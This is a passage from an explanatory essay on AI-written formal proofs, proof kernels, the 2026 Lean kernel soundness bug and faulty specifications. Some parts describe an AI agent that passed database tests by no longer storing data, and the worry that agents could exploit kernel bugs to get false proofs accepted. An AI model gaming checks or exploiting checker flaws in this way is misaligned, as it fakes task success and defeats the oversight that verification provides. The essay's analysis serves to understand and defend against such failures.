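The theorems apply to particular RISC-V programs, each running as a single thread in a model of Linux with a fixed memory limit of 64 MB. The limit is easy to raise in the specification, but Claude would have to redo the proof. Anthropic does not claim that the libraries are free of other bugs.

Few people run these exact programs. Anthropic acknowledges that most run the libraries on x86 or ARM processors and link them dynamically to glibc, the usual C library on Linux. A dynamically linked program loads shared code when it starts instead of containing its own copy. A proof about RISC-V machine code does not apply to x86 code, because the compiler produces different instructions for each processor type.

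*Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026), published a week later, presents a Lean proof that covers a complete run of an x86 program containing glibc. Two security firms began the project in mid-September, using frontier models with expert guidance. Even tiny programs are difficult to verify on x86, because glibc picks routines optimised for the processor in use. The string-comparison function the firms had to verify has 316 instructions, compared with 14 in the simpler RISC-V library that Anthropic used. The proof still assumes one thread, static linking and a specific processor.

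A more basic limit is that each theorem covers one fuzz test, and a fuzz test uses the library in only one way. Lim and colleagues illustrate this with a made-up but typical library for reading data in chunks. Before copying a chunk, the library should check that the chunk is no longer than the remaining data, but it compares the chunk's length with the size of the whole file instead. The fuzz test opens a file, reads once and closes it. On a first read, the remaining data is the whole file, so the check is correct and the no-crash theorem is true. If a program reads 40 bytes twice from a 64-byte file, however, the second read also passes the check, even though only 24 bytes remain, and it runs 16 bytes past the end. The shop's refund bug is the same mistake, since a second refund of 60 euros passes if the program compares it with the original charge.

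Many bugs never cause a crash. For example, a program that refunds too much money can keep running normally. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) describes logic bugs, in which software breaks the implicit rules for how it should work, and notes that they rarely trigger the failures that automated tools detect.

The theorems are still valuable, since memory errors are among the most dangerous bugs and the proofs exclude them for every input in range. But people who call a program "verified" should specify which properties were proved. In *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, Keles (2026) is optimistic about the technology and thinks AI has made it mainstream. Yet he says he doesn't have much confidence that a system is correct when he hears it called formally verified, because people use the phrase for very different things.

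### Proofs of what a program does

Models can also prove more than the absence of crashes. In the October study, Claude proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, the compression library, conforms to the published standard for the format. It also wrote an interpreter in Rust for part of Python and used Verus to prove that the interpreter matched a formal description of Python's behaviour. The researchers ran over 1.7 million random programs through both this interpreter and CPython, the standard implementation. OpenNET reports that the results agreed in 99.95% of cases, which leaves about 850 disagreements, all of them known edge cases.

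In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) used a system built at Google DeepMind to verify security properties of the compiled ARM code of the library behind Signal, the encrypted messaging app. One property is forward secrecy, which means that someone who steals today's keys still can't read earlier messages. Another is post-compromise security, which means that a conversation becomes secure again some time after a theft. It would be hard to write a fuzz test for either property, because a program that leaks its keys doesn't crash.

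People guided the agent that wrote the specifications for Signal, and a team of other agents then found the proofs autonomously. The proofs are about 6.5 million lines of Lean, 250 times as long as the 26,000 lines of specifications and processor rules that people have to trust. But 26,000 lines is still a lot to read, and an error in them could undermine the whole result.

All of these libraries except the Python interpreter existed before anyone tried to verify them. With new code, a model can write the program and its proof together. The best-known case is lean-zip, an AI-written Lean version of zlib. De Moura (2026) shows in *Lean* that lean-zip's round-trip theorem holds at every compression level and guarantees that decompression finishes without an error. zlib compresses data in stages, first replacing repeated passages with references to earlier ones and then giving common symbols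 shorter codes. A proof can handle the stages separately, because if undoing each stage recovers its input, undoing them all in reverse order recovers the original data.

The AI was a general-purpose model with no special training in theorem proving. De Moura says its version passed zlib's test suite before the AI proved anything. The tests still matter because this theorem alone doesn't guarantee that the output is smaller than the input or that other programs can read it.

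lean-zip's 32,000-line proof is about a twentieth of the length of a typical proof in the October study, though its theorem covers much more than crashes. Writing new code in a language designed for proofs is clearly easier than reasoning about old C code one instruction at a time. The drawback is that the guarantee then depends on Lean's own compiler and runtime, the support code that every Lean program needs. The author of *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* fuzzed lean-zip 105 million times and found a buffer overflow in that runtime. Another flaw, in a part of lean-zip with no specification, let a malicious file disable the program. The fuzzer found no memory errors in the code that the proofs covered.

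### Software that is still hard to prove

*How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* gives three reasons why verification is rare: some languages lack the necessary tools, proofs are expensive, and developers may not adopt verified code even when it exists. AI has helped most by making proofs cheaper, and quick progress on x86 suggests it is also helping with tools. But some kinds of software are hard to verify for other reasons.

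Concurrent programs do several things at once, and the order of their steps can vary from run to run. Two threads of ten steps each can interleave in 184,756 ways. The shop's refund invariant would have to hold through every possible interruption, including one between checking the total and updating it. Neither the 239 theorems nor the x86 proof covers multithreaded programs.

AI is already useful for finding concurrency bugs. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) discusses a case in which Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code, had Claude formalise one of Anthropic's software packages. A couple of short prompts led to 16 proposed fixes for bugs and race conditions, where the outcome depends on which of two operations happens first. Tolmach and Klaus call this good news but point out that it doesn't show that the code is correct, because a checked proof applies only to the mathematical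 model the AI built.

People can close that gap with a second proof. Category Labs' *finding bugs that frontier models miss* describes how the company's engineers modelled a blockchain's rules for account balances in Rocq and found a flaw before anyone had written the code. They later proved that the C++ function was equivalent to their model. xv6, an operating system used for teaching, now has a full proof of its concurrent machine code. The proof covers every interleaving of eight processor cores with devices and interrupts, though xv6 is far smaller than Linux.

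Long-lived state causes a related problem even with a single thread. To cover every legitimate use of a library, a proof has to handle any number of calls in any permitted order. Lim and colleagues wrote test programs that make such sequences of calls for 29 libraries and released them as open challenges. They expect these programs to be harder to prove than fuzz tests, because the effects of each call persist into later ones.

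Programs that use floating-point numbers, as most scientific calculations do, are hard to verify because the arithmetic rounds. In standard 64-bit arithmetic, (10¹⁶ + 1) − 10¹⁶ gives 0 because there is no room to store the final 1. The usual rules of algebra therefore no longer apply, and the step in the sum proof that rearranged i(i + 1)/2 + (i + 1) might fail. The specification must include an allowed error, and the prover must track how errors build up through the calculation. The big AI projects of 2026 prove facts about memory, data formats and secrecy, so they provide little evidence about whether models can do this well.

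User interfaces are hard to verify mostly because they are hard to specify. The shop can prove that its refund button is inactive when there is nothing left to refund, but it can't easily state as a formula that customers will understand why. Better provers don't help with this, though developers can limit the problem by keeping the rules about money in a separate part of the program and verifying only that part.

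AI may have made the most difference when requirements change. A small change to a program can break a long proof, and a team that releases new code every day could never rely on experts to repair proofs by hand. Models are good at such repairs. In the October study, Claude had to prove a new theorem every time it patched a library. A team at Microsoft is verifying the company's cryptographic library, and the slides from Lean quote Son Ho as saying, "We are verifying code faster than we can write it."

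A model can't repair a specification in the same way when the requirement changes. If the shop decides to give unhappy customers an extra 10 euros, `refunded ≤ charged` is no longer the right rule. Someone has to decide whether the 10 euros applies once per payment or once per complaint, and a model could prove the code correct under either reading.

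## How proof checkers let people trust proofs they did not write

The proofs in the October study run to about 180 million lines, and nobody will read them. People can still rely on them because a small program, the proof kernel (unrelated to an operating-system kernel such as seL4), checked every step. As long as the proof kernel works, mistakes in the other tools that help produce a proof, including the tactics and the language model, can't cause a wrong proof to be accepted.

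### How a kernel checks a proof

Lean's kernel is a type checker that works much like the TypeScript checker that checked `newTotal`. In Lean, a mathematical statement is a type, and a proof of it is a value of that type. A proof of "if A then B" is a function that takes a proof of A and returns a proof of B.

Suppose the shop's agent has to prove that refunded + r ≤ charged at a point where the code has already tested that r ≤ charged − refunded. Call the result of that test `h`. Suppose also that the library contains a theorem called `move`: for all integers a, b and c, if a ≤ c − b, then b + a ≤ c. The agent's whole proof is then `move r refunded charged h`, and the kernel checks it in four steps:

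1. It looks up `move` among the theorems it has already accepted.
2. It replaces a, b and c with r, refunded and charged, which gives "if r ≤ charged − refunded, then refunded + r ≤ charged".
3. It works out what `h` proves and compares that with the "if" part. The two match.
4. It concludes that the expression proves refunded + r ≤ charged, and compares this with the statement the agent had to prove. These match too, so it accepts the theorem.

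If the code had compared r with the original charge, `h` would prove only r ≤ charged, and the third step would fail.

The kernel sometimes has to calculate before it can compare two statements. For example, it has to work out 2 + 2 to recognize that 2 + 2 ≤ 5 and 4 ≤ 5 are the same statement. It also has to check the definition of every new data type, because a badly formed one can introduce a contradiction. The kernel could then be made to accept a proof of any statement, including false ones.

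A user can export a Lean proof to a file that contains every definition and theorem it depends on, written in the kernel's minimal language. *Type Checking in Lean 4*, an online book about the kernel, explains how a separate program can check the whole file and display the theorems for people to read. The user doesn't have to trust the exporter, because if it garbles the proof, the checker either rejects the file or displays the wrong theorem.

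### Two ways to keep the rest of the system out

In the 1970s, Robin Milner worked out one way to protect a kernel, in a proof assistant called LCF. LCF makes "theorem" an abstract type, so only a few functions inside the kernel can create a theorem. Each rule of logic has its own function. One, for example, takes the theorems "if A then B" and A and returns the theorem B. A tactic can call these functions in any order, but the programming language's type checker rejects any tactic that tries to make a theorem another way. Once LCF has a theorem, it can discard the steps that led to it.

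Lean and Rocq keep the steps of a proof. Their tactics build a proof term, such as `move r refunded charged h`, and the kernel checks the finished term. Such systems meet the de Bruijn criterion, named after Nicolaas de Bruijn, who began the Automath proof system in the late 1960s. A complicated program may search for the proof, but its result must be a proof in a small language that a simple checker can verify. Anyone can write another checker for that language. *Type Checking in Lean 4* describes this as more than an afternoon's work but within reach of an amateur.

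The two designs have much in common. Peano Lab's *The kernel and the De Bruijn criterion* describes LCF's central idea, which modern systems have kept, as untrusted search on top of a tiny trusted base. Proof terms are also less complete than they seem. Mathematics and Computation (2016), a blog on logic, argues that a proof assistant needs an efficient way to communicate and verify proofs, but doesn't have to store them in raw form. For example, Rocq's terms leave out calculations like 2 + 2, and the checker redoes them.

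The difference matters most when the author is untrusted. A second person can check a stored proof term as data, without running the author's code. If no proof term is stored, that person has to rerun the author's proof script, which is a program.

### Proof-carrying code

Computer scientists have also used this idea to decide whether to run a stranger's program. In *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, Necula and Lee (1996) considered an operating system that has to run code from an untrusted source. A typical example is a packet filter, which picks out certain network messages. Accepting only code digitally signed by a trusted person would not rule out that person's mistakes, and checking every memory access while the filter runs would slow it down.

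Necula and Lee instead had the code's author attach a proof. The owner of the computer publishes a safety policy, such as a list of the memory that outside code may read or change. The author sends the machine code together with a formal proof that it obeys the policy. The owner's computer then derives a logical formula from the code. If the formula is true, the code obeys the policy. The computer checks that the attached proof proves this formula and, if it does, runs the code at full speed with no further checks. George Necula developed this into a general framework, proof-carrying code, in 1997.

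If someone alters the code in transit, the computer derives a different formula and the old proof will usually fail. If the proof still works, the altered code also obeys the policy. The owner doesn't have to trust the author, the author's compiler or the network, but does have to trust the policy, the program that derives the formula, and the proof checker, which make up the trusted computing base. Andrew Appel later proposed a "foundational" version in which the proof starts from a mathematical description of the processor, so the owner no longer has to trust a separate program to derive the formula. The no-crash theorems in the October study also rely on a model of the processor.

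Proof-carrying code gives the author the hard job of finding the proof. In the 1990s, this difficulty mostly limited the technique to simple properties that a special compiler could prove automatically. A language model can now attempt much harder proofs, so the shop could require a proof with every change its agent submits.

### The Lean kernel bug of July 2026

All of this relies on the checker, which is also a program and can have bugs. On July 25, 2026, Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted Lean "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture. According to the conjecture, if we start with any positive whole number and repeatedly halve it when it is even or triple it and add one when it is odd, we will eventually reach 1. Starting from 6, we get 3, 10, 5, 16, 8, 4, 2, 1. Lean accepted this disproof even though it was wrong.

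Lean's kernel was missing a check on one complicated kind of data-type definition, as de Moura (2026) explains in *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576*. The mistake was in the program, not in the logic it implements. On July 28, Kiran Gopinathan reduced the disproof to a short proof of a contradiction and reported it, and Lean's developers pushed a fix an hour later.

A second checker, nanoda, had also accepted the disproof. Nanoda is an independent Lean kernel that Chris Bailey wrote in Rust. It didn't have the same bug, but a version from a week earlier had an unrelated one, and the disproof exploited both. The developers had already fixed the nanoda bug after a report from Jeremy Chen. Kumar believes the timing was a coincidence, but can't rule out that the AI model had seen Chen's report. The notes to the corrected release, The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2 (2026-07-28)*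 (2026), advise people who might receive malicious proofs to update nanoda as well.

A third checker, lean4lean, had the same bug as the official kernel because its author had copied the design of the faulty part from the kernel. Two checkers protect against each other's mistakes only where their authors worked independently.

People using AI models found other kernel bugs at about the same time. Patrick Hulin found one with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol, and *Lean 4.32.1 (2026-07-22)* fixed it less than a week before Gopinathan's report. After that report, Daniel Selsam at OpenAI used an AI specialised in cybersecurity to find several more. Most of the bugs could do harm only if malicious code ran in the same process as the kernel. But *Lean 4.33.0 (2026-08-10)* lists two, including the Collatz one, that could let a false proof pass Lean's recommended procedure for untrusted proofs unless the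 user also ran a checker such as nanoda.

These discoveries raised the worry that an agent with a hard theorem to prove might look for a kernel bug instead. Joachim Breitner, a Lean developer, writes in *Riemann con leche* (2026) that he has not seen an agent try this without being explicitly asked to. But a training process that rewards a model whenever the kernel accepts its proof would also reward it for finding a bug.

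### Are stored proofs worth their weight?

Lawrence Paulson, who created the proof assistant Isabelle, thinks the Collatz affair counts against storing proof terms. In *Why is it all in the kernel?* (2026), he compares this to towing a spare car everywhere in case the first one breaks down, then finding that the spare doesn't work either. He knows of no case in which an independent checker caught a false proof that a proof assistant's own kernel had accepted, and the stored proofs use a lot of memory.

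Paulson also objects to how much Lean's kernel has to do. Lean builds complicated data types into the kernel, and the Collatz bug was in that part of it. Isabelle and related systems, such as HOL Light, start from a few basic axioms and derive the rest. To define lists of numbers, for example, they construct the smallest set that contains the empty list and every list made by adding a number to the front of a list already in the set. They then prove from the axioms that this set behaves as lists should. This takes far more work, but the work happens outside the kernel, so a mistake in it can't cause a contradiction. Paulson acknowledges that Isabelle has had soundness bugs too. For people who care most about soundness, he recommends HOL Light, HOL4, or Candle, a verified version of HOL Light.

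De Moura favors proof terms because they separate the checker from the author's code. After the Collatz affair, some people suggested restricting the Lean features that let users send definitions directly to the kernel. De Moura calls this misguided, because an attacker could also write Lean's output files directly or change Lean's memory while it runs. The kernel has to reject bad definitions by itself, in its own process, which it can do only if it receives the whole proof. He also points out that the false disproof needed two different bugs in two programs.

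Paulson's point about the missing track record became weaker two days after he made it, when de Moura reported that nanoda caught all the mistakes Selsam's search had found in the official kernel. But Selsam found them by looking for bugs, not because nanoda had rejected a theorem somebody was relying on.

His point about size is harder to answer. A kernel that does less has fewer places for bugs, and Lean's developers have since begun to simplify theirs. But even a small kernel needs to be kept separate from untrusted code. For proofs that an AI wrote and nobody reviewed, that separation seems worth the extra memory it uses.

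### Kernels with proofs of their own

Lean's developers responded more fully in October. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (De Moura, 2026) presents `lake check`, a command that exports a project and rechecks it inside a sandbox, using the official kernel without the software that normally surrounds it. A stricter mode, `--paranoid`, adds four other kernels: nanoda, lean4lean, con-leche and con-ron. It also runs a version of the official kernel that stops if its memory becomes corrupted, whereas an ordinary version might return a wrong answer.

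Con-leche is the first Lean kernel that is both written in Lean and proved consistent. Claude wrote the program and the proof under Breitner's close supervision. Breitner had started on July 30 with another plan, a checker that would justify each step with a separate small proof in set theory. He gave up this plan after a few weeks because the extra bookkeeping made the checker too slow. Con-leche avoids this bookkeeping because its proof covers every possible input in advance.

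The proof shows that any collection of definitions and theorems con-leche accepts has a model in set theory. In the model, each type is a set and each value of the type is a member of that set. A false statement corresponds to the empty set, and a proof of it would have to be a member of that set. The empty set has no members, so con-leche can't accept a proof of a false statement.

Even with this assurance, con-leche executes 31% fewer processor instructions than the official kernel when checking Mathlib, Lean's main library of mathematics. With eight threads, it checks all 2.5 million lines in about 100 seconds.

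The consistency proof first assumes that the set theory used for the model is consistent. Some assumption like this is unavoidable, because Kurt Gödel proved in 1931 that no consistent formal system that includes basic arithmetic can prove its own consistency. *HOL in HOL* (Kirchner, 2026) shows that Isabelle's logic can prove the consistency of a version of itself without the axiom of infinity, but needs an extra axiom from set theory to do so for a version with it.

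Lean's logic is stronger. It is consistent exactly when standard set theory with infinitely many "inaccessible cardinals" added is consistent, a known result that *Reflections on Trusting Lean* (Bresolin and Mamino, 2026) builds on. These cardinals are infinite sets so large that the standard axioms can't prove they exist. Someone could reject them on philosophical grounds, but a contradiction in the extended theory would be far more surprising than another programming mistake in a kernel.

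Trusting con-leche is also somewhat circular, because the official Lean kernel checked the proof about it. A bug in that kernel could in principle have let a faulty proof through, though people can check the proof with other kernels too.

The last assumption is that Lean's compiler and runtime run con-leche correctly. This can fail, since a fuzzer testing lean-zip found a buffer overflow in the runtime. Breitner therefore used AI to translate con-leche into a Rust version, con-ron, and then used a tool called Aeneas to prove that con-ron follows the same checking algorithm. To get past both kernels, a false proof would probably have to exploit one bug in Lean's compiler or runtime and another in Rust's.

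### Checking Fermat and Riemann

Large AI-written proofs have made this a practical matter. Hales (2026), in *What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover*, recalls that the formal proof of the Kepler conjecture, about the densest way to pack spheres, took about 20 work-years and 500,000 lines. In September 2026, Anthropic announced a 13-million-line Lean proof of Fermat's Last Theorem that AI had written in 11 days.

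In *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a post on the blog Xena, the mathematician Kevin Buzzard lists four questions to ask about a Lean proof. They are whether the formal statement means what people think it means, whether the code compiles, whether it proves that statement, and whether the proof is valid.

A proof of this size can be hard to compile. Anthropic asked Buzzard to look at the Fermat proof, and he put it in a sandbox because AI-written code could in theory delete his files. His computer soon ran out of memory. He told Anthropic that he couldn't confirm anything until he saw the code compile, and the company lent him a machine with 96 cores and 500 GB of memory, on which it did compile.

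A Lean project can compile without proving the intended theorem. Lean's editor puts a blue double check mark beside a proved theorem, even if the proof relies on another theorem that is unfinished. Lean treats each gap as an extra axiom, so users can find gaps by running `#print axioms`, which lists every axiom a theorem depends on. According to *Validating a Lean Proof* in The Lean Language Reference, the list should contain only three standard axioms. One makes equivalent statements equal, one is the axiom of choice, and one lets users treat related objects as the same. The reader has to accept any other axiom without proof.

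A dishonest author can get around these checks, because Lean runs the author's code while it compiles the project. The Lean Language Reference classes unreviewed AI-generated proofs as possibly malicious and recommends a tool called comparator. The user writes the theorem's statement in a separate, trusted file. Comparator compiles the submitted project in a sandbox and exports the proof. It then rechecks the exported proof outside the sandbox, where the author's code can't interfere, and confirms that the theorem is exactly the one in the trusted file.

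The biggest test of these methods came on November 20, 2026, when Levent Alpöge released an AI-written proof of the Riemann hypothesis, a conjecture from 1859 about the distribution of prime numbers. The proof has 17 million lines of Lean in 175,187 files. The exported version takes up 61.6 GB. Andrew Sutherland of MIT began checking it the same day, and recorded these results in *Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026):

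| Checker | Result on the first day | Time |
|---|---|---|
| con-leche, newest version | accepted | 3 min 15 s on 64 threads |
| nanoda | accepted | 27 min 42 s on 80 threads |
| lean4lean, file by file | accepted, after a higher step limit for five files | not given |
| Official kernel, file by file | accepted | not given |
| Official kernel, exported proof | still running on one thread | not given |
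| con-leche and con-ron, as shipped with Lean | declined to check | not given |

The shipped versions of con-leche and con-ron stopped because they didn't yet support one data type in the proof, not because they had found an error. The proof used only the three standard axioms, and an option in con-leche confirmed that the proof's main theorems matched the trusted statements.

*Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026), by the Lean and Mathlib communities, certified the proof the next day, after going through Buzzard's four questions. By then, dozens of people had compiled the project and obtained the same export file, and the official kernel, con-leche, con-ron and several independent checkers had accepted it. These checks establish that the theorem is true but don't explain why. The two communities look forward to mathematicians' efforts to explain the proof's new ideas.

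Proofs may soon be too large for these tools. De Moura mentions one Lean project with more than 50 million lines and proposals for libraries with over a billion, and says the current approach to external checking doesn't scale that far. At the Riemann proof's rate of about 3.6 kB per line, the export of a billion lines would be roughly 3.6 terabytes. Lean's developers are working on a more compact file format and on checkers that recheck only what has changed.

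## Whether the specification says what was meant

A proof kernel checks a proof against a formal statement. It can't check whether the statement says what people meant, so a flawless proof can still be worthless. *claimcheck* (Amster, Baker and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with sorting. Suppose the specification for a program that sorts a list of numbers requires the output to be in increasing order. A verifier would correctly accept a program that always returns an empty list, because an empty list has no two numbers in the wrong order.

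### Repairing the sorting specification

As a formula, the requirement is that out[i] ≤ out[j] for all positions i < j. We can repair it by looking for a bad output that it allows, adding a condition that excludes that output, and looking again. For the input [3, 1, 3, 1], this goes as follows:

| Conditions on the output | An output they allow |
|---|---|
| It is in increasing order | [] |
| It also has the same length as the input | [0, 0, 0, 0] |
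| It also contains the same values as the input | [1, 1, 1, 3] |
| It also contains each value as often as the input does | only [1, 1, 3, 3] |

With the last condition added, every input has exactly one possible output. The first number has to be the smallest in the input, because otherwise the smallest would come later and be out of order. For the same reason, the second number has to be the smallest of the rest, and so on.

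The specification may still not match what was meant. If the shop sorts its refund records by amount, the owner may expect the older of two separate 60-euro refunds to come first, but the specification allows either order.

*DafnyCert* (Silva, Amaral and colleagues, 2026) calls a specification strong if it allows exactly one output for every permitted input, weak if it allows more than one for some input, and vacuous if it permits no inputs. A weak specification can be deliberate, as with the rule that 0 ≤ refunded ≤ charged, which leaves most of the program's behaviour open. A strong specification can still be wrong. For example, "the same numbers in decreasing order" allows only one output, but it is the wrong specification for a program meant to sort in increasing order.

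### How specifications go wrong

A weak specification covers the right subject but still allows wrong answers. One function in the benchmark VeriEquivBench should compute the fewest rungs to add to a ladder so that no step is longer than a given distance. Its specification, which the benchmark had labelled strong, requires only that the answer is not negative. Silva and colleagues replaced the function's body with a line that returns 0, and it still passed verification. For a ladder whose only rung is at height 463, with steps of at most 1, the right answer is 462.

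A theorem of the form "if A, then B" is true whenever A is impossible, whatever B is. Tolmach and Klaus cite an example from the benchmark FaithformBench, which gave a model the deliberately wrong step "3ˣ = 5, so 3ˣ⁺² = 51" (the right answer is 45). The model translated it into Lean with x as a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, so the false step became a provable theorem.

A wrong definition is harder to notice because the statement that uses it can look right. In the vericoding benchmark of Bursuc and colleagues, one Dafny specification relies on an undefined function for splitting text into lines. The model that translated the specification into Verus filled in the missing definition with a default value.

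Even a correct definition can mislead a reader who expects a different one. *The Limits of Machine-Certified Mathematics in the Age of Artificial Intelligence* (Karazoupis, 2026) gives a deliberately misleading Lean version of the Goldbach conjecture, here the claim that every even number n from 6 upwards is the sum of two odd primes p and q. The Lean statement requires (p + q) − n = 0 instead of p + q = n. Subtraction on Lean's natural numbers stops at zero, so 6 − 20 is 0, and p = q = 3 satisfies the statement for every such n. All six kernel checks accepted the proof. Each kernel was correct, so adding more would not have helped.

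Specifications can also leave out a requirement. The code of IronFleet, a verified distributed system written in Dafny, ensured that each request took effect exactly once, but the specification didn't require this. Silva and colleagues recount how other researchers used a small patch to switch off the removal of duplicate requests, and the broken system still verified. In a payment system, such a bug could charge a customer twice. Lorica (2026), in *Maybe we've been thinking about verification backwards*, describes an AI agent that exploited a similar gap in a set of tests. It made a database six times faster by no longer storing the data.

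Finally, the specification may be right while the model of the machine or program is wrong. CompCert, the verified C compiler, modelled the PowerPC processor with no limit on the size of a constant inside an instruction, although a real instruction has a fixed number of bits for it. AI systems make larger mistakes of this kind. According to Tolmach and Klaus, researchers asked Claude to model how Etcd, a database copied across several machines, keeps its copies in agreement. Claude essentially reproduced the model from the paper that introduced the general method. The result passed every check but had little to do with Etcd's code. Across leading AI models, such descriptions scored nearly 100% on syntax but about 46% on matching the real system. The no-crash proofs in the October study also have modelling limits, such as assuming a single thread, but the researchers disclosed them.

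### Statements in AI-written mathematics

Mathematics is a good place to look for mismatches between a formal statement and its intended meaning, because experts know what the theorems should say. In his post on Xena, Buzzard gives an example that looks like Fermat's Last Theorem, stating that aⁿ + bⁿ ≠ cⁿ for all natural numbers a, b, c and n with n ≥ 3. In Lean, the natural numbers include 0, so a = b = c = 0 is a counterexample. Lean accepts the statement, but nobody can prove it. Trying to prove a statement therefore exposes mistakes that make it false, but not mistakes that make it too easy to prove.

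Buzzard also looked at the papers that OpenAI released in October 2026. Of the 290 that came with Lean code, about 38 had code that did not even state the paper's main theorem. One paper proves Lech's multiplicity conjecture, open since 1960, but the main theorem in its Lean code is only Corollary 5.4 of the paper. OpenAI had never claimed otherwise, but readers who see Lean code next to a paper may wrongly assume that it covers the main theorem.

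Other statements are too long to check easily. The company Axiom announced a formal proof of the classification of finite simple groups, which lists all the basic building blocks of finite symmetry. About 5,600 lines of AI-generated code define the terms in the theorem, including all 26 exceptional "sporadic" groups. Buzzard has not met anyone who claims to have checked those definitions carefully. He thinks the best evidence that the statement is right is that Axiom's system proved it. This is evidence because a mistake that left a sporadic group off the list would make the theorem false. But a definition loose enough to admit extra groups would make the theorem easier to prove.

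Broader tests also show many mismatches. *Beyond Compilation* (Zhang, Gallardo Candela and colleagues, 2026) examined an agent that translated graduate-level mathematics into Lean. Tolmach and Klaus report that 89.5% of the agent's statements compiled but only 60.5% were faithful.

Sometimes the human wording already differs from what was meant, before anyone formalises it. The Navier–Stokes equations describe how fluids flow, and there is a million-dollar prize for settling whether they can "blow up", with the flow becoming infinitely fast at some point. OpenAI's AI proved in September 2026 that they can, but only with a contrived external force. As Howlett explains in *Did OpenAI solve the wrong Navier-Stokes problem?*, the official problem statement from 2000 explicitly allows such a force, though most experts had assumed there would be none. Even a perfect formalisation of the official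 statement would have kept this loophole.

### Can a machine translate mathematics faithfully?

The Navier–Stokes proof is also the main case study in *Navier-Stokes lost in translation* (Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen, 2026), which distinguishes between two tasks. In the first, people already have a correct formal statement, and an AI system uses an informal proof to guide its search for a formal proof. In the second, the AI has to translate a whole text, including every definition and argument, without changing its meaning.

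A valid Lean proof doesn't show that the informal proof it came from is right. Bastounis and colleagues gave ChatGPT a wrong proof that x³ − x² − x + 1 ≥ 0 for x ≥ −1. The proof factored the expression as (x − 1)(x + 1)², but the correct factorization is (x − 1)²(x + 1). ChatGPT returned a valid Lean proof with the correct factors. They found similar differences between the paper and the Lean code in the Navier–Stokes work. One lemma in the paper bounds a function using four extra derivatives, while the closest Lean version needs five and is therefore weaker. They don't claim that the paper is wrong, and they accept that the Lean code proves the main theorem.

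For the second task, they prove that no algorithm can always succeed. Suppose a textbook gives a polynomial p and defines n as the smallest natural number for which p(n, x₁, …, x₉) = 0 has no solution in natural numbers. It then sets r = 1/(n + 1) and states that (r + 1)² = r² + 2r + 1. This statement is trivial if r exists. But if the equation has a solution for every natural number n, then the textbook's n doesn't exist, so r is undefined and the statement has no faithful translation.

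Lean may not reveal the problem, because one standard function for finding the smallest member of a set returns 0 when the set is empty. A translation that uses this function would set n = 0 and r = 1, and the remark would compile.

A faithful translator therefore has to know whether n exists. For any computer program, we can construct a polynomial that has a solution for n exactly when the program stops on input n. The polynomial then lacks a solution for some n exactly when the program runs forever on some input. No algorithm can determine whether this happens for every program, even with a hypothetical device that solves Turing's halting problem. Bastounis and colleagues produce still harder versions, without limit, by making the definition of n more complicated. This is why they call faithful translation "harder than any computational problem".

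The theorem is correct, but it matters less in practice than this phrase suggests. It concerns a translator that must either translate each text or declare it untranslatable. It doesn't apply to a translator that may answer "I don't know", just as Rice's theorem doesn't rule out a sound checker that rejects some good programs. A translator could also use a different Lean function for the smallest member of a set, one that requires a proof that the set isn't empty. The textbook's remark would then fail to compile until somebody supplied that proof.

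The mistakes people find have little to do with such undecidable questions. According to Bastounis and colleagues, Meta claimed in spring 2026 to have translated 26 mathematics textbooks into Lean. Meta reported success on 56% of the target statements in one book, but a member of the Lean community could not find one without a fatal error. Other AI systems had done most of the checking for faithfulness. A more relevant obstacle is that ordinary language has no formal definition, so there is no automatic way to compare a sentence with its formal version, as *Symbolic Informalization* (2026) points out. This affects easy sentences as well as hard ones.

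How much this matters depends on what people want from a proof. Mathematicians want to learn from the argument and reuse its lemmas, so a mismatch in a lemma matters to them. The shop needs only the final theorem about refunds, so it doesn't matter if the agent's English explanation uses a different argument from the proof.

### Testing a specification

People can test a specification much as they test a program, by checking that it allows correct outputs and excludes wrong ones. In the sorting example, each of the first three versions would fail this test because it allows a wrong output shown in the table above.

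*VerusEval* (Wang, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) measured how well this works on 13,716 files in which language models had written the specification and the proof. Verus accepted about 7,100 of them, but tests on examples then exposed problems in 23.6% of those. One specification was for a function that returns the shortest list in a collection, but it didn't require the result to come from the collection. For a collection containing [1, 2] and [3], it allowed the answer [9].

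Passing the tests was weak evidence that a specification was right. Verus could prove only 63.2% of the passing specifications equivalent to a reference specification. The researchers also made 943 deliberate changes to good specifications. The tests caught 81.8% of these changes, but none of the 72 that tightened the requirements on the output, because the code happened to meet the tighter requirements.

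Overall, only 42.3% of the accepted files passed the tests on examples, a check for empty specifications and a comparison with the reference. The specifications were probably better than this figure suggests, since many files failed only because Verus couldn't complete a proof of equivalence. About a quarter had a more concrete fault. The models included GPT-4o and Llama 4, so newer ones may do better.

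Another method is to change the code and check whether it still verifies. If it does, and it gives a different output for some input, the specification is weak. Silva and colleagues found the weakness in the ladder specification this way, and their tool automatically exposed 91.9% of the 3,323 weak specifications in their collection. Anyone can recheck the result by running Dafny on the original and altered programs.

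When no such change turns up, people can try to prove consequences they expect from the specification. For example, sorting should preserve the length of a list. The first version of the sorting specification doesn't imply this, so the proof fails and reveals the gap. In a particularly informative check, Silva and colleagues call a function twice with the same input and ask Dafny to prove, from the specification alone, that the outputs are equal. Dafny proved this automatically for 515 of 587 strong specifications. Checking only for empty specifications is much less useful, and in VerusEval it flagged just 104 of the accepted files.

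Two people or models can also write specifications independently and try to prove them equivalent. In VerusEval, comparison with a reference flagged nearly every file that the examples had caught and many more. But the reference can also be wrong. Wang and colleagues picked out 61 suspicious references for review and found likely defects in 36. After they repaired one of these, 10 of the 11 specifications that had disagreed with the original turned out to be equivalent to the repaired version. Comparison helps least when both writers misread the requirement in the same way, which is more likely if they are copies of the same model.

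Amster and colleagues built Claimcheck, a tool that checks whether a specification matches the original request. One model translates the specification into plain English without access to the request, and another compares the translation with the request. If the first model had the request, its translation might reflect the request rather than the specification. When the researchers gave it the request, the share of bad specifications caught fell by 6.0 to 8.8 percentage points.

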